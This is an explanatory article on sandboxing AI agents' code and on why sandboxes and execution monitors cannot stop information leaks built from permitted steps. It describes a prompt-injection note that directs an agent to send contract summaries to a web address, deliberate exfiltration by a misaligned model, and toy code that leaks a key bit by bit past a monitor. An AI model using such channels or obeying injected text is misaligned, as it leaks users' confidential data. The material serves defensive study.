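# Sandboxing code written by AI agents, and why sandboxes cannot enforce purity or stop information leaks

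## What are agents' programs allowed to do, and what do purity and leakage mean?

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that lets it act, for example by reading files, searching the web or running commands. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) adopts the programmer Simon Willison's definition that an agent "runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal". Increasingly, the tool is a programming language. The agent writes a short program, a computer runs it, and the agent reads the output. People check few of these programs before they run, so operators confine them in a sandbox, a restricted environment that limits which files, network hosts and other system resources a program can use.

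A sandbox controls which resources a program can access. Controlling what the program does with a file it is allowed to read requires other tools, which researchers in operating systems and programming languages have been building since the 1960s and 1970s.

### From the model to the machine and back

A language model only produces text. The software around it, called the harness, turns some of that text into actions. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how this works in Codex CLI, OpenAI's coding agent that runs on the user's computer. The harness assembles a prompt from standing instructions, a list of tools and the user's request, and sends it to the model. The model returns either a final answer or a tool call, such as a request to run the shell command `cat README.md`, which prints a file. The harness runs the command, appends the output to the prompt and sends the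 longer prompt back. This repeats until the model returns a final answer, which can take hundreds of tool calls.

Whatever a command prints therefore becomes part of the model's context, the text that the model works from. If the model runs in another company's data centre, printing something sends it there. Codex also resends the conversation so far with every request, so it sends each printed line repeatedly until the harness condenses the history.

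### Why agents write programs

In the older approach, an agent acts through single tool calls. The model names one function and its arguments in JSON, a standard text format for data, the harness runs the function, and the result goes back to the model before the agent can do anything else. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* gives the example of an agent that fetches a meeting transcript from Google Drive and attaches it to a customer record in Salesforce. (MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is a common standard for connecting agents to tools.) With single calls, the whole transcript passes through the model twice, which can add 50,000 tokens, or word fragments, for a two-hour meeting. A script can move the transcript from one service to the other without the model reading it. An agent that writes code can also load descriptions of only the tools it needs, which reduced token use from 150,000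 to 2,000 in Anthropic's example.

Controlled tests mostly confirm the savings, though not for every model. *Beyond Plain MCP* (Rai, 2026) tested three open-weight models on 119 office-style tasks using simulated services such as billing, calendars and chat. Scripts used 70 to 90 percent fewer tokens than single calls. Success rose from 85.7 to 99.2 percent for Qwen3.8-27B and from 36.1 to 55.5 percent for Nemotron-3-Nano, while the gain for Gemma-4-26B was too small to distinguish from chance. *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) compared code with JSON across 14 OpenAI and Anthropic models, and code matched or beat JSON in 11 of them. The three that did worse with code, GPT-4o, GPT-4.1 and GPT-5.4-mini, kept writing the characters `\n` where a line break belonged, which crashed their scripts. That test scored only whether the model named the right functions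 and arguments, and the functions were not connected to real services.

The benefit of code also depends on the task. Code helps when there are many steps or bulky data. Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling*, a page of developer documentation, reports that the feature cut billed input tokens by 38 percent on a project-management benchmark with 75 tools. On customer-service tasks with one or two calls per turn, it left scores unchanged and cost about 8 percent more. Patel and colleagues still describe JSON calls as the dominant interface in deployed systems, but the two formats overlap. Codex's shell tool, for example, takes a JSON call whose argument is a command, which is itself a program.

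### The contract example

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) illustrates the problem with a company that wants an agent to compare versions of its confidential contracts and summarise the changes. The agent's model runs in the cloud, and its provider counts as an outsider, so the text must not reach that model or anyone else without authorisation. Wording inside a contract also should not steer what the agent does.

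The job is possible because the cloud model can write the program without seeing the data. In Python, with `load`, `diff` and `local_model` standing for tools that the harness supplies, the program might be:

```
old, new = load("2025.txt"), load("2026.txt")
summary = local_model("Summarise the changes", diff(old, new))
open("summary.txt", "w").write(summary)
```

Here `local_model` is a second language model that the company trusts with the text. It has no tools and no memory of earlier prompts. The user opens the summary file, and the cloud model needs only a signal that the program finished. The company wants to be sure that the program takes these steps and no others, without reading every program the agent writes.

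Adding the line `print(summary)` would undo the arrangement, because the harness would put the printed text into the next prompt. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* presents keeping intermediate results where the code runs as a privacy benefit, since the model receives only what the code logs or returns. This is a useful default but a weak barrier here, because the model that should not get the text also writes the code that does the logging.

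Where the code runs also matters. With Anthropic's programmatic tool calling, the model's script runs in a container, an isolated environment with its own files, on Anthropic's side of the interface. When the script calls one of the developer's tools, it pauses until the developer's application sends the result to Anthropic, then resumes with it. Only the final output enters the model's context, but the intermediate results have still left the developer's premises. To keep them in-house, the contract company would have to run the program on its own machine.

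An agent might write the damaging line by mistake. Models, like programmers, print intermediate values to find bugs. A script can also leak text without a `print`. If it tries `float("4.2m")` on a sum from a contract, Python stops with an error message that repeats `4.2m`, and a harness normally returns error messages to the model along with other output. A misaligned model, one that pursues aims its developers or users did not intend, might send the text out on purpose. An outsider might also cause the leak through prompt injection, which is text in the data an agent reads that gets the agent to follow an attacker's instructions. For instance, the attacker could claim in a note in the project folder that company policy requires sending a copy of every summary to some web address.

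Prompt injection works because a model receives its instructions and the data it reads in one stream. Pirch and colleagues examined four widely used general-purpose agents (OpenClaw, IronClaw, Nanobot and NemoClaw) and found that all four put trusted and untrusted data into a shared context. Odersky and colleagues cite a real case of the resulting harm, in which the security researcher Johann Rehberger got user data out through Anthropic's own file-upload interface.

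Odersky and colleagues design for the worst case, a cloud model that cooperates fully with the attacker. This assumption also covers honest mistakes and prompt injection, because a control that holds against a determined adversary also holds against a careless one. A control that catches only mistakes may not stop a deliberate leak. For example, a filter that searches outgoing text for phrases from the contracts would catch a stray `print` but miss a model that spelled the phrases backwards.

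### Processes, effects and flows

A process is a running program with its own memory and permissions. The line `subprocess.run(["python3", "compare.py"])` starts one, and the new process normally inherits the permissions of the process that started it. A process can compute freely within its own memory, but it must make a system call to reach anything outside. A system call is a request to the kernel, the core of the operating system. Python's `open("2026.txt")` leads to such a request, and the kernel either returns a handle to the file or denies the request. Many sandboxes work by restricting which of these requests the kernel grants.

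A side effect is anything a computation does besides returning a result. `open("summary.txt", "w").write(summary)` has one because it changes the disk. A pure computation has no side effects, and its result depends only on its inputs, as with `def words(text): return len(text.split())`. Python's `time.time()` changes nothing, but it is not pure because its result depends on the clock. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, also count reading a file as an effect, so a function that processes a contract can be pure only if another part of the program reads the file and passes in the text.

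A whole agent program is rarely pure, because it needs side effects to do things like save the summary. It is more useful to require local purity, which means that one part of the program must be pure while the rest may have side effects.

Information flow is the influence of one piece of data on another. Denning and Denning (1977) distinguished two forms of it in *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*. One is explicit flow, in which the program passes data along directly, as in `excerpt = contract[:200]`. Computing a value from a secret is also an explicit flow, as in `l := h + 2`, the example in *Verifying Type Soundness for Nontransitive Information Flow Security* (2026), where the public variable `l` receives the secret `h` plus two.

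An implicit flow passes information through a decision. Suppose `flag` starts at 0 and the program runs `if "penalty" in contract: flag = 1`. This line copies none of the contract's text, but anyone who reads `flag` afterwards knows whether the word occurs, even if the assignment never ran, because a 0 means the word is absent. A loop that tests every bit of every character this way can rebuild the whole text. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) points out that the order in which an agent calls its tools can also reveal something about the data that led it to choose that order.

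A label is a mark on data that records how secret or how trustworthy it is, and it passes to whatever a program derives from that data. When a program combines two items, the result takes a label at least as strict as both, written `label(summary) = join(label(old), label(new))`. A summary of a confidential contract and a public template is therefore confidential. Text from a language model is harder to label because it is hard to tell which parts of the prompt influenced a given sentence. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes a default of joining the labels of everything that went into the generation, which errs on the side of caution.

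A capability is an unforgeable value that gives its holder the right to use a resource. The function `def save(out, text): out.write(text)` writes to whatever file its caller passes as `out`. But `out` is not a real capability in Python, because `save` could also call `open` with any path. In the file library that Zhou and colleagues built, code can read a file only with a special `Path` value. It can get one by narrowing a directory it already holds, but not from a plain string such as `"/etc/passwd"`.

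### Rules about resources and rules about computations

"This program may not write outside the project folder" is a rule about a resource. A sandbox can check each write request separately, because the request includes a path that is either inside the folder or outside it. The check needs no other information about the program, and the same rule can cover the whole process from start to finish.

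The rule "this function may read the contract but may not send anything" applies to one computation. The rest of the program may need to send things, if only a notice to the cloud model that the job is done. Disconnecting the whole process would then break the task, but leaving it connected would let the function send data too. Whether the rule applies depends on which part of the program is acting and whose data it carries.

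*Language-Based Information-Flow Security* (Sabelfeld and Myers, 2003) observes that access control restricts the release of information but not its propagation. Once a program has read a file, it can pass on the contents through error or malice. To protect a secret with file permissions alone, the owner would have to grant access only to programs that never leak, and the permission system cannot identify those programs.

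Zhou and colleagues list some rules about computations that an agent's user might want. One is that data from customer A must never go to customer B, even though the agent serves both. Another, which concerns trustworthiness rather than secrecy, is that every entry an agent adds to a bibliography must come from a trusted database. A resource rule can let the agent write only to the bibliography file, but it would also allow a reference that the model made up, because adding one takes the same kind of request to the same file.

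### A pure function can still give the secret away

Even if the company could guarantee that every function which handles contract text is pure, the text could still leak. A pure function cannot contact a server or write a file, but `def same(text): return text` is pure and returns the entire contract to its caller, which may print it.

Restricting the type of a program's result may not stop it from leaking information. Zhou and colleagues describe a calculator agent whose program must return an integer and have no effects. If a visitor asks the agent to delete the server's files and then compute a factorial, the program cannot delete the files, because deletion is an effect. But if the program also had a contract as an input, it could leak the contract's full text, since `int.from_bytes(text.encode(), "big")` packs a whole document into one large integer that the recipient can unpack.

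A function can also be impure without leaking what the contract says, because purity concerns what a computation does while it runs, and secrecy concerns who can learn something from it. For example, `def log(text): open("log.txt", "a").write("compared\n")` has a side effect, but it adds the same line to the log whatever the contract says.

Purity still helps keep data secret because data can then get out mainly through the return value, which a program can guard. Odersky and colleagues therefore keep each confidential document in a sealed container, which applies only pure functions to its contents and puts each result in another sealed container. The agent's program can produce a summary this way, but if it prints the summary, the cloud model receives only a row of asterisks. The functions must be pure because one with network access could send the text out before returning a result to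 seal.

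## How do the sandboxes of coding agents restrict a program?

Suppose the company in the contract example runs Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, on an employee's Linux laptop, and the cloud model has saved its program as `compare.py`. To start the program, the model returns a call to the Bash tool, which runs shell commands, with the command `python3 compare.py`. The harness then has to decide whether to run the command, and with what access.

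### Asking the user

Claude Code originally asked for the user's approval before it changed a file or ran most commands, with exceptions for harmless ones such as `echo`, according to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025). A prompt protects users only if they think about it, and the command `python3 compare.py` tells them little about what the program does unless they also open the file.

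People also stop paying attention to permission prompts, a problem known as approval fatigue. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (2026) reports that users approved roughly 93 percent of prompts and paid less attention to each one as they saw more of them. The approval rate alone does not prove carelessness, since most of what a coding agent proposes may well be harmless.

With a sandbox, the user makes most of these decisions once, in advance, by choosing which folders and network hosts commands may reach. The harness can then run commands inside those limits without asking. Anthropic found that sandboxing cut permission prompts by 84 percent in its internal use. That figure does not measure how many harmful commands the sandbox stopped. Many of the prompts that remain are requests to go beyond the limits.

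### One command in Claude Code

Claude Code's sandbox is off until the user turns it on with `/sandbox`. It works on macOS, Linux and WSL2, the Linux environment inside Windows. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* describes how the sandbox handles commands once it is on.

First, the harness compares the text of the command with the user's permission rules. If a rule denies the command, the harness doesn't run it. In the sandbox's auto-allow mode, most other commands go ahead without a prompt, though an `rm` command that would delete the home directory still triggers one. The check covers only the text of the command, so if the command is `python3 compare.py`, it doesn't cover what the script does.

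Next, the harness runs the command inside a restricted environment set up by bubblewrap, a small open-source program. Bubblewrap uses namespaces, a Linux kernel feature that gives a group of processes its own view of part of the system. A separate view of the file system, for example, can make the project folder writable and the rest of the disk read-only, and can show an empty folder in place of one the user wants to hide. A separate view of the network does not include the laptop's network connection. Any process that the script starts inherits the same views.

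Python now runs the script. The call `open("2026.txt")` succeeds because the file is visible inside the sandbox. The script can also write `summary.txt` because that file is in the project folder. It cannot write to `~/.bashrc`, a file of commands that the shell runs when it starts. The sandbox also blocks writes to Claude Code's own settings files, so a command cannot loosen the rules that confine it.

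The default is much looser for reading. A sandboxed command can read almost any file on the computer, including `~/.ssh` and `~/.aws/credentials`, where developers often keep login keys. Users can block such paths with the `denyRead` setting. The programming blog Arrange Act Assert recommends starting with a newer setting, available since version 2.1.187, that blocks named credential files and removes sensitive environment variables before each command runs.

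If the script contacts a server, its traffic goes through a relay to a proxy outside the sandbox. The proxy, a program that forwards network traffic, compares the requested host name with an allowlist, the list of hosts that the policy permits. The list starts empty, and Claude Code asks the user when a command needs a new host. If `local_model` runs on another machine in the company, for example, the user has to approve that machine's name.

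The proxy does not decrypt traffic, so it cannot read what a program sends to an approved host and must rely on the host name that the program supplied. Anthropic warns that approving a domain as broad as `github.com` can allow data to leak, and it lets companies substitute their own proxy that decrypts and inspects the traffic.

If the sandbox caused a command to fail, the model may try to run it again outside the sandbox, which normally requires the user's approval. Administrators can disable this option. If bubblewrap is missing, Claude Code by default shows a warning and then runs commands without a sandbox, but administrators can change this too.

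On macOS, Claude Code uses Seatbelt, a sandboxing framework that comes with the operating system. Seatbelt attaches a list of rules to a process, and the kernel checks operations against the rules as they happen, without rearranging what the process sees. This can affect which files are protected. Anthropic also offers its sandbox as a separate package, the sandbox runtime, which can wrap a whole program and blocks writes to certain sensitive files. Anthropic says that on macOS the block also covers matching files that appear during the session. On Linux, the runtime lists the files to block once, at launch, so it misses any that a command creates later.

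### What the Linux kernel can check

Sandboxes on Linux commonly combine three kernel features: namespaces, Landlock and seccomp. Namespaces change a process's view of the system. Landlock and seccomp refuse some of the process's requests without changing that view.

Landlock lets a process give up access rights for itself and its children without an administrator's help. The process lists the directories it may read or write, and when it later tries to open a file, the kernel checks whether the file is under one of them. Newer versions can also restrict which TCP ports a process connects to (a port is a number that identifies a service on a machine) and how it communicates with other processes. Landlock has no rules for host names, so it can allow encrypted web traffic in general but cannot limit it to one company's server.

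Seccomp runs a small filter each time a process makes a system call. The filter receives the number that identifies the call and the raw values of its arguments, which is enough to restrict some calls. For example, the first argument of `socket`, which creates a connection point, is a number that specifies the type of connection, so a filter can block one type and allow the others. Claude Code has an optional seccomp filter that blocks Unix sockets, the type that connects programs on the same machine. Access to these sockets is risky because powerful services listen on them. According to Anthropic, access to the socket of the container system Docker effectively gives a program access to the whole host.

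A seccomp filter cannot check which file a program is opening. When Python opens `2026.txt`, it passes the system call a pointer, which is the address in memory where the file name is stored, and seccomp filters cannot follow pointers. They cannot check the destination of `connect` either, because its network address is also passed by pointer. Sandboxes therefore use namespaces or Landlock for rules about files, and use seccomp to block whole kinds of system call that a program should not need.

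### OpenAI's Codex

Codex also runs commands in the user's existing environment, but it turns its sandbox on by default. OpenAI's *Sandbox* gives approval fatigue as one reason for the sandbox. The user chooses one of three modes. In `read-only`, Codex can inspect files but needs approval to edit them or run commands. In `workspace-write`, it can edit files in the workspace, normally the project folder, and run routine commands there. `danger-full-access` removes the restrictions.

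A separate approval policy determines when Codex has to ask the user. With `on-request`, it asks when it needs to go beyond the sandbox. With `never`, it does not ask and has to work within the sandbox's limits. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes another option, in which a second AI agent, instead of the user, reviews requests to leave the sandbox, but not actions that stay inside it.

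OpenAI has been replacing the modes with permission profiles, which combine rules for files and for network hosts. OpenAI's *Permissions* sets out the format. A profile for the contract company might extend the built-in `:workspace` profile like this:

```
default_permissions = "contracts"

[permissions.contracts]
extends = ":workspace"

[permissions.contracts.filesystem.":workspace_roots"]
"originals" = "read"
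"personnel" = "deny"
```

Commands could then write in the project folder, but they could not change anything in `originals` or even read `personnel`. A rule for a more specific path overrides a broader one, and if two rules name the same path, `deny` takes precedence. A profile can also deny access to all files that match a pattern, such as those ending in `.env`, which often contain passwords. On Linux and Windows, Codex may have to search for matching files before the sandbox starts.

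OpenAI's *Inside the Codex sandbox* explains the reasoning behind Codex's defaults. Codex can write in the workspace so that it can edit source code without asking each time. But `.git` and `.codex` stay read-only, because `.git` can contain hooks, which are scripts that Git runs automatically, and `.codex` contains Codex's own settings. Codex has broad read access because compilers and build tools need libraries and configuration files from elsewhere on the machine. OpenAI accepts that this may also expose files containing API keys, the passwords that programs use for online services. Network access is off, which stops commands from directly uploading what they have read, but also from downloading packages.

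| Default | Claude Code's Bash sandbox | Codex on the user's computer |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox | Off until the user enables it | On |
| Reads | Almost the entire computer | Most files that the user can read |
| Writes | Current working folder | Workspace, except protected folders such as `.git` and `.codex` |
| Network | No host until the user approves it | Off |
| When the system cannot enforce the limits | Warns, then runs commands without a sandbox | Refuses to run the command |

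According to OpenAI, turning on network access in Codex gives commands full access unless the profile also lists hosts. A proxy enforces any such list, much as in Claude Code.

The mechanism depends on the platform. Codex uses Seatbelt on macOS. On Linux it combines bubblewrap with seccomp and can fall back on Landlock where compatibility requires it. On Windows, its strongest sandbox runs commands under separate user accounts with few privileges and adds file permissions and firewall rules. A weaker sandbox needs no administrator rights but isolates the network less well.

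Codex also has a cloud version, which runs in containers that OpenAI manages. During setup, the container can use the network and any passwords the user has configured, for instance to install packages. Before the agent starts, Codex removes the passwords and, by default, disconnects the network.

A command can still do harm within these default limits. OpenAI points out that an agent could alter project code that the user's editor later runs outside the sandbox. The company relies partly on the model's training to prevent this.

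### Sandlock and decisions at run time

The permissions a program needs can change while it runs. For example, a single command might install a project's packages, which requires the network, and then run tests that may not need it. Fixed rules would have to leave the network on for both. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) presents a Linux sandbox for agents that separates rules it can fix in advance from decisions it must make at run time.

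Sandlock has the kernel enforce every rule it can decide before the program starts. Landlock enforces the rules about directories, ports and communication between processes, and seccomp blocks the system calls that are never acceptable. For the remaining decisions, Sandlock uses a seccomp feature called user notification. The kernel pauses a system call and passes it to a supervisor, an ordinary process outside the sandbox, which decides what to do.

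Unlike a seccomp filter, the supervisor can read a program's memory. When the program calls `connect`, the supervisor copies the destination address from that memory, checks the copy against the allowlist and uses the copy to make the connection itself. It must not let the original call continue after the check, because the kernel would read the address from memory again, and another part of the program might have changed it in the meantime. Sandlock refuses any request that it cannot decide on safely.

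This arrangement allows much narrower network rules. A policy can limit the program to certain kinds of request to certain pages on one server, although for encrypted traffic the program has to accept a certificate that lets Sandlock's proxy read the requests. The application that runs the agent can also supply a function that monitors the program and tightens the rules while it runs, for example by withdrawing network access when the tests begin. Sandlock can set file changes aside until the user accepts or discards them, and it can run the stages of a pipeline in separate sandboxes.

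Sandlock's overhead was small in Wang and Zheng's measurements on a six-core machine. It added about 5 milliseconds to the start of a command. Running `echo` took about 6 milliseconds in total under Sandlock and 44 times as long under Docker. The Redis database handled 75,200 write requests per second under Sandlock and 75,500 without it, a difference within the normal variation between runs. Under Docker, Redis reached about 76 percent of its unrestricted speed.

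Sending network traffic through the supervisor causes a larger relative slowdown, raising the time for a short message and its reply from 20 to 55 microseconds. The added delay is negligible for an agent whose calls to a language model take at least a tenth of a second, but it could matter for a program that exchanges many small messages.

There is less evidence for Sandlock's security. Wang and Zheng ran ten checks, such as whether a program could read a folder outside its permissions, and Sandlock followed the policy in all ten. These checks show that the rules work in ordinary cases, but they do not test Sandlock against someone trying to break it. Its threat model also excludes kernel bugs. Wang and Zheng recommend a small virtual machine instead when one machine runs hostile programs from many customers.

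### Containers and small virtual machines

A container has its own files and network settings, but its processes still make system calls to the host's kernel, as do processes under bubblewrap, Landlock or Seatbelt. A serious bug in the host's kernel could therefore let a program escape any of these sandboxes. A virtual machine has its own kernel, and a program that takes control of that kernel still has to get past the hypervisor, the software that keeps the virtual machine separate from the host.

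Virtual machines used to start slowly, which is a problem for an agent that runs dozens of short commands. A microVM is a stripped-down virtual machine that starts much faster. Wang and Zheng list approximate startup times of 100 milliseconds for Firecracker, a microVM system that Amazon uses for its cloud services, and 300 milliseconds for a Docker container that runs without administrator rights. They list about 200 milliseconds for gVisor, which runs a second kernel as an ordinary program between a container and the host. Tools like bubblewrap take about 30 milliseconds. An agent that stays in one microVM for a whole session also waits for startup only once.

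Docker Sandboxes gives each agent its own microVM. According to Docker's *Isolation layers*, the agent can act as administrator inside the microVM because security depends on the hypervisor, not on restrictions inside the microVM. The agent also gets a private copy of Docker's container engine, so it can run `docker` commands inside the sandbox, whereas users of Claude Code's Bash sandbox have to run them outside it. All of the agent's TCP traffic, which includes ordinary web requests, goes through a proxy on the host that enforces the network policy. The proxy can also add API keys to requests, so the keys don't have to enter the microVM.

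A separate kernel does not protect the files shared with the agent. By default, the command `sbx run` gives the agent read and write access to the current folder, and the agent's changes appear on the host immediately. Some of those files, such as build scripts and editor settings, can run code on the host later. In clone mode, the agent works on a private copy of the project and the user decides which changes to bring back, but the agent can still read everything in the folder, including password files that the user has told Git to ignore.

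Setting up a separate machine also takes work. OpenAI gives this as a reason for running Codex's commands in the user's existing environment, since developers customise their laptops heavily and some tools have to run on the host. In *SideKernel*, Prasakis (2026) surveyed 68 users of coding agents, of whom 26 were using a sandbox and 35 had never used one. The most common complaints were about networking, having to set up tools and logins again, and sharing files with the host. The survey was informal and drew on Prasakis's professional and university contacts, so the proportions may not hold for developers in general.

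Prasakis then built SideKernel, a microVM sandbox for Claude Code on Macs, to remove these obstacles. It shares the current folder automatically, copies in the user's Claude Code extensions and keeps the login credentials on the host. Its network control is simpler than Docker's. The user can block all connections except those to Anthropic's interface, but cannot approve individual hosts. In a comparison of 23 features related to the complaints, SideKernel and Docker Sandboxes each had 19, while three other products had 12. Prasakis also designed the comparison, which counted convenience features and did not measure resistance to attack.

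How well a sandbox protects depends on what it allows as well as its type. Prasakis considers containers weaker than microVMs but finds Seatbelt harder to rank, because it shares the host's kernel yet enforces a specific policy there. A microVM with a writable project folder and an open network would protect the contracts less than a Seatbelt profile that blocks network access and writes to the folder.

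Boundaries also fail because of bugs. On 30 November 2026, Docker fixed a flaw in Docker Sandboxes that, according to the trade magazine PCQuest, could expose API keys to destinations the developer had not approved. The flaw was in how the product authorised the use of credentials, so keys could leak without a breach of the microVM.

### What runs outside the sandbox

Claude Code's sandbox applies to shell commands and the processes they start, but not to the agent's built-in tools for reading and editing files. Anthropic notes that MCP servers, the programs that connect an agent to outside tools, also run directly on the host. So do hooks, which are commands the user configures Claude Code to run at certain points, such as after each edit.

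In Claude Code, the sandbox setting `denyRead` stops `cat` from printing a file, but the built-in file reader follows permission rules instead. A permission rule that denies reading a folder blocks both, because Claude Code merges those rules into the sandbox's configuration. Sandboxed commands inherit environment variables by default, including any passwords stored in them. When Claude operates apps on the user's screen, it works on the real desktop rather than in a sandbox.

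Codex has similar gaps. Its permission profiles govern commands on the user's machine, while MCP servers, connections to other apps and browser tools have separate controls. According to OpenAI, Codex always asks before an outside tool takes an action that the tool advertises as destructive, so the safeguard depends on the tool's own description. With Docker Sandboxes, some local MCP servers run on the host, outside the microVM.

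Users can close many of these gaps by sandboxing the whole harness. They can run Claude Code in the sandbox runtime, a container or a virtual machine, so that the same limits apply to its file tools, hooks and local MCP servers as to shell commands. Anthropic considers the Bash sandbox alone insufficient when nobody is supervising the agent.

The harness still has to reach its model. If the model runs in the cloud, the boundary must allow a connection to the provider, and Anthropic states that isolation does not change what Claude Code sends there. A sandbox therefore cannot stop the leak through `print(summary)`, because the printed text leaves over a connection the agent needs.

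## Why can a sandbox not stop a leak made of permitted steps?

The leak through `print(summary)` takes three operations, and the company's sandbox has to permit all three if the agent is to do its job. In simplified form, they are:

```
read(2026.txt)                     the script has to compare the contracts
write(standard output, summary)    the harness collects the script's output
send(model provider, next prompt)  the cloud model needs each new prompt
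```

None of these operations breaks a rule about files or hosts. The agent may read the file and may call the cloud model. The company objects only to the movement of data from the file to the model, and this movement never crosses the boundary that the sandbox guards. Odersky and colleagues use the contract example to make this point about sandboxes in general.

A stricter sandbox could inspect the data. Sandlock's supervisor can read a program's memory, and a proxy that decrypts traffic can read the messages. These checks catch crude leaks, such as a contract sent word for word. But some leaks would get past even a monitor with access to every system call, every byte of every message and the secret itself, as two very short programs prove.

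### Two programs with the same system calls

Suppose a file holds a secret key, and `send` passes text to an outsider over a connection that the sandbox allows.

```
# Program A
key = open("key.txt", "rb").read()
send("0")

# Program B
key = open("key.txt", "rb").read()
send(str(key[-1] % 2))
```

Program A reads the key, perhaps for some local purpose, but is harmless because it sends the same message whatever the key is. Program B sends the key's last bit.

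Suppose the last bit is 0. Both programs open `key.txt`, read the same bytes and send the text `0`. Their system calls are identical in number, order and content. A monitor that uses only those calls receives the same input in both cases, so it must make the same decision. If it blocks the message, it stops a harmless program, and if it allows the message, the outsider receives the last bit of the key from Program B.

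A monitor that allowed `0` and blocked `1` would not stop the leak, because an outsider who knew the program would take silence to mean 1. It would also block a harmless program that always sends `1`. The monitor could stop the leak by replacing every message with `0`, but then no program could report anything after reading the key.

An agent can run hundreds of commands in a session, so a version of Program B that sends a different bit of a 256-bit key on each run would leak the whole key in 256 runs.

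The proof applies to monitors that judge a program by its system calls. Someone who reads the code of Program B can easily spot the leak, because the code shows what the program would send if the key were different. The system calls of a single run don't contain that information.

### Noninterference

Noninterference means that changing the secret inputs never changes what an unauthorised observer sees. Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined it in 1982 for systems with several users. In their version, removing every command from high-clearance users must not change what low-clearance users see.

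For a single program, let `l` stand for the public inputs, `h` for the secret inputs and `P(l, h)` for everything the outsider observes when the program runs on them. If the program makes no random choices, noninterference requires that

```
for all l, h1, h2:   P(l, h1) = P(l, h2)
```

The condition compares two runs that have the same public inputs but may have different secrets. Program A satisfies it because the outsider always observes `0`. Comparing a run whose key ends in 0 with one whose key ends in 1 proves that Program B violates the condition, although either run would look acceptable on its own.

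In the contract example, the contracts' text is the secret input, and the outsider observes whatever reaches the cloud model. A program that always prints `finished` satisfies noninterference. A program that runs `print(summary)` violates it, because different contracts produce different summaries. A program can also violate it by accident. If it crashes on a sum written as `4.2m` and otherwise prints `finished`, the crash reveals something to the cloud model about how the contract is written, even if the harness withholds the error message.

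Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, give a version for whole executions, which they call observational determinism. They represent a run as a trace `t`, the sequence of states that the system goes through, and a system as the set `T` of all its possible traces. The condition is

```
for all t, t' in T:   t[0] =L t'[0]  implies  t ≈L t'
```

Here `t[0]` is the first state of a run, `=L` means that two states look the same to the outsider, and `≈L` means that two whole runs do. If two runs look the same to the outsider at the start, they must continue to look the same. The definition's one exception is that a program may leak information by failing to finish. The finer controls also have to deal with running time and other covert channels, which raise similar problems.

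Strict noninterference forbids some releases that a user wants. For example, *Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) describes a scheduling assistant that may tell others when its user is free but not why the user is busy. The paper's rule therefore compares only runs in which the free and busy times, the authorised part of the secret, are also the same. Suppose the only difference between two runs' inputs is that a busy slot is a confidential interview in one and an ordinary meeting in the other. If the assistant offers different meeting times in the two runs, its offers depend on something it had no permission to reveal. This rule is looser than strict noninterference, but checking it still takes two runs.

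### What a monitor can enforce

The two-program proof is a small case of a general result. In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider asked which policies a mechanism can enforce by watching a program's steps and stopping the program before it breaks a rule. He called such mechanisms execution monitors. They include firewalls, security kernels and most other controls built into operating systems and hardware.

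An execution monitor knows what the program has done so far in the current run. It does not know what the program will do next, or what it would have done with other inputs. Schneider derived three conditions from this that any enforceable policy must meet:

1. The policy can be checked one run at a time, without reference to other runs.
2. If the beginning of a run is unacceptable, nothing that happens later can make the run acceptable. The monitor can't wait for a later step to put things right, because the program might stop first.
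3. A run that breaks the policy does so after a finite number of steps.

Policies that meet these conditions are safety properties, which require that some identifiable bad thing never happens. "Never write outside the project folder" is a safety property because a single write outside the folder violates it. Access control in general is a safety property, so a sandbox can enforce it.

Information flow does not meet the first condition. We can see why by adding a third program that reads the key, ignores it and sends the result of a coin toss. An outsider learns nothing about the key from the message, because 0 and 1 are equally likely whatever the key is. For a program that makes random choices, noninterference requires that the probability of each message not depend on the secret. The table lists every combination of key and message, and the programs that can produce each one.

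| Last bit of the key | Message | Program A | Program B | Coin toss |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | `0` | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| 0 | `1` | No | No | Yes |
| 1 | `0` | Yes | No | Yes |
| 1 | `1` | No | Yes | Yes |

The coin-toss program is harmless, so a monitor that never blocks harmless programs has to accept all four kinds of run. Those include both runs that Program B can produce, although Program B leaks the bit every time. Schneider argues similarly that a set of runs can satisfy an information-flow policy while a subset of it does not. This cannot happen with a safety property, because if every run in a set is acceptable, so is every run in any subset.

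The theorem also applies to several execution monitors working together. Schneider showed that they enforce the combination of their separate policies, which is again a safety property. A sandbox that combines namespaces, Landlock, seccomp and a proxy can therefore enforce more rules about resources than any one of them alone, but it cannot enforce exactly the rule that no information flows from the contracts to the provider.

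Schneider excluded compilers and theorem provers from his definition, and so from the theorem, because they analyse a program's code and can draw conclusions about all its possible runs. He left open how much more they can enforce.

### Hyperproperties

Clarkson and Schneider later developed a theory of policies that concern several runs at once. A trace property is a set of acceptable runs, and a system satisfies it if each of its runs is in the set. A hyperproperty is a set of acceptable systems, each itself a set of runs. Some hyperproperties don't involve secrecy, such as "the mean response time over all runs is below one second." This is a hyperproperty because whether one slow run is acceptable depends on how fast the others are.

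Every information-flow policy that Clarkson and Schneider examined was a hyperproperty and not a trace property. They do not claim this for all such policies, because researchers have no agreed definition of information flow. *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties* (Finkbeiner, 2025), a later overview of the field, also treats information flow as something that cannot be determined from a single execution.

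Observational determinism belongs to a relatively manageable class called 2-safety. If a system violates a 2-safety property, two finite runs are always enough to prove it. This makes it possible to turn the question about two runs into a question about one run of a larger program, a technique called self-composition. The checker makes a second copy of the program, renames its variables so that the copies cannot interfere, and gives both the same public inputs but independent secrets. For Program B, the combined program amounts to

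```
out1 = key1[-1] % 2
out2 = key2[-1] % 2
assert out1 == out2
```

The original program is secure if the assertion holds for every pair of keys. Here the assertion fails for any pair whose last bits differ. For Program A, both outputs are 0, so the assertion always holds. Clarkson and Schneider proved that the same reduction works for violations that take three or more runs to demonstrate, using one copy of the program per run.

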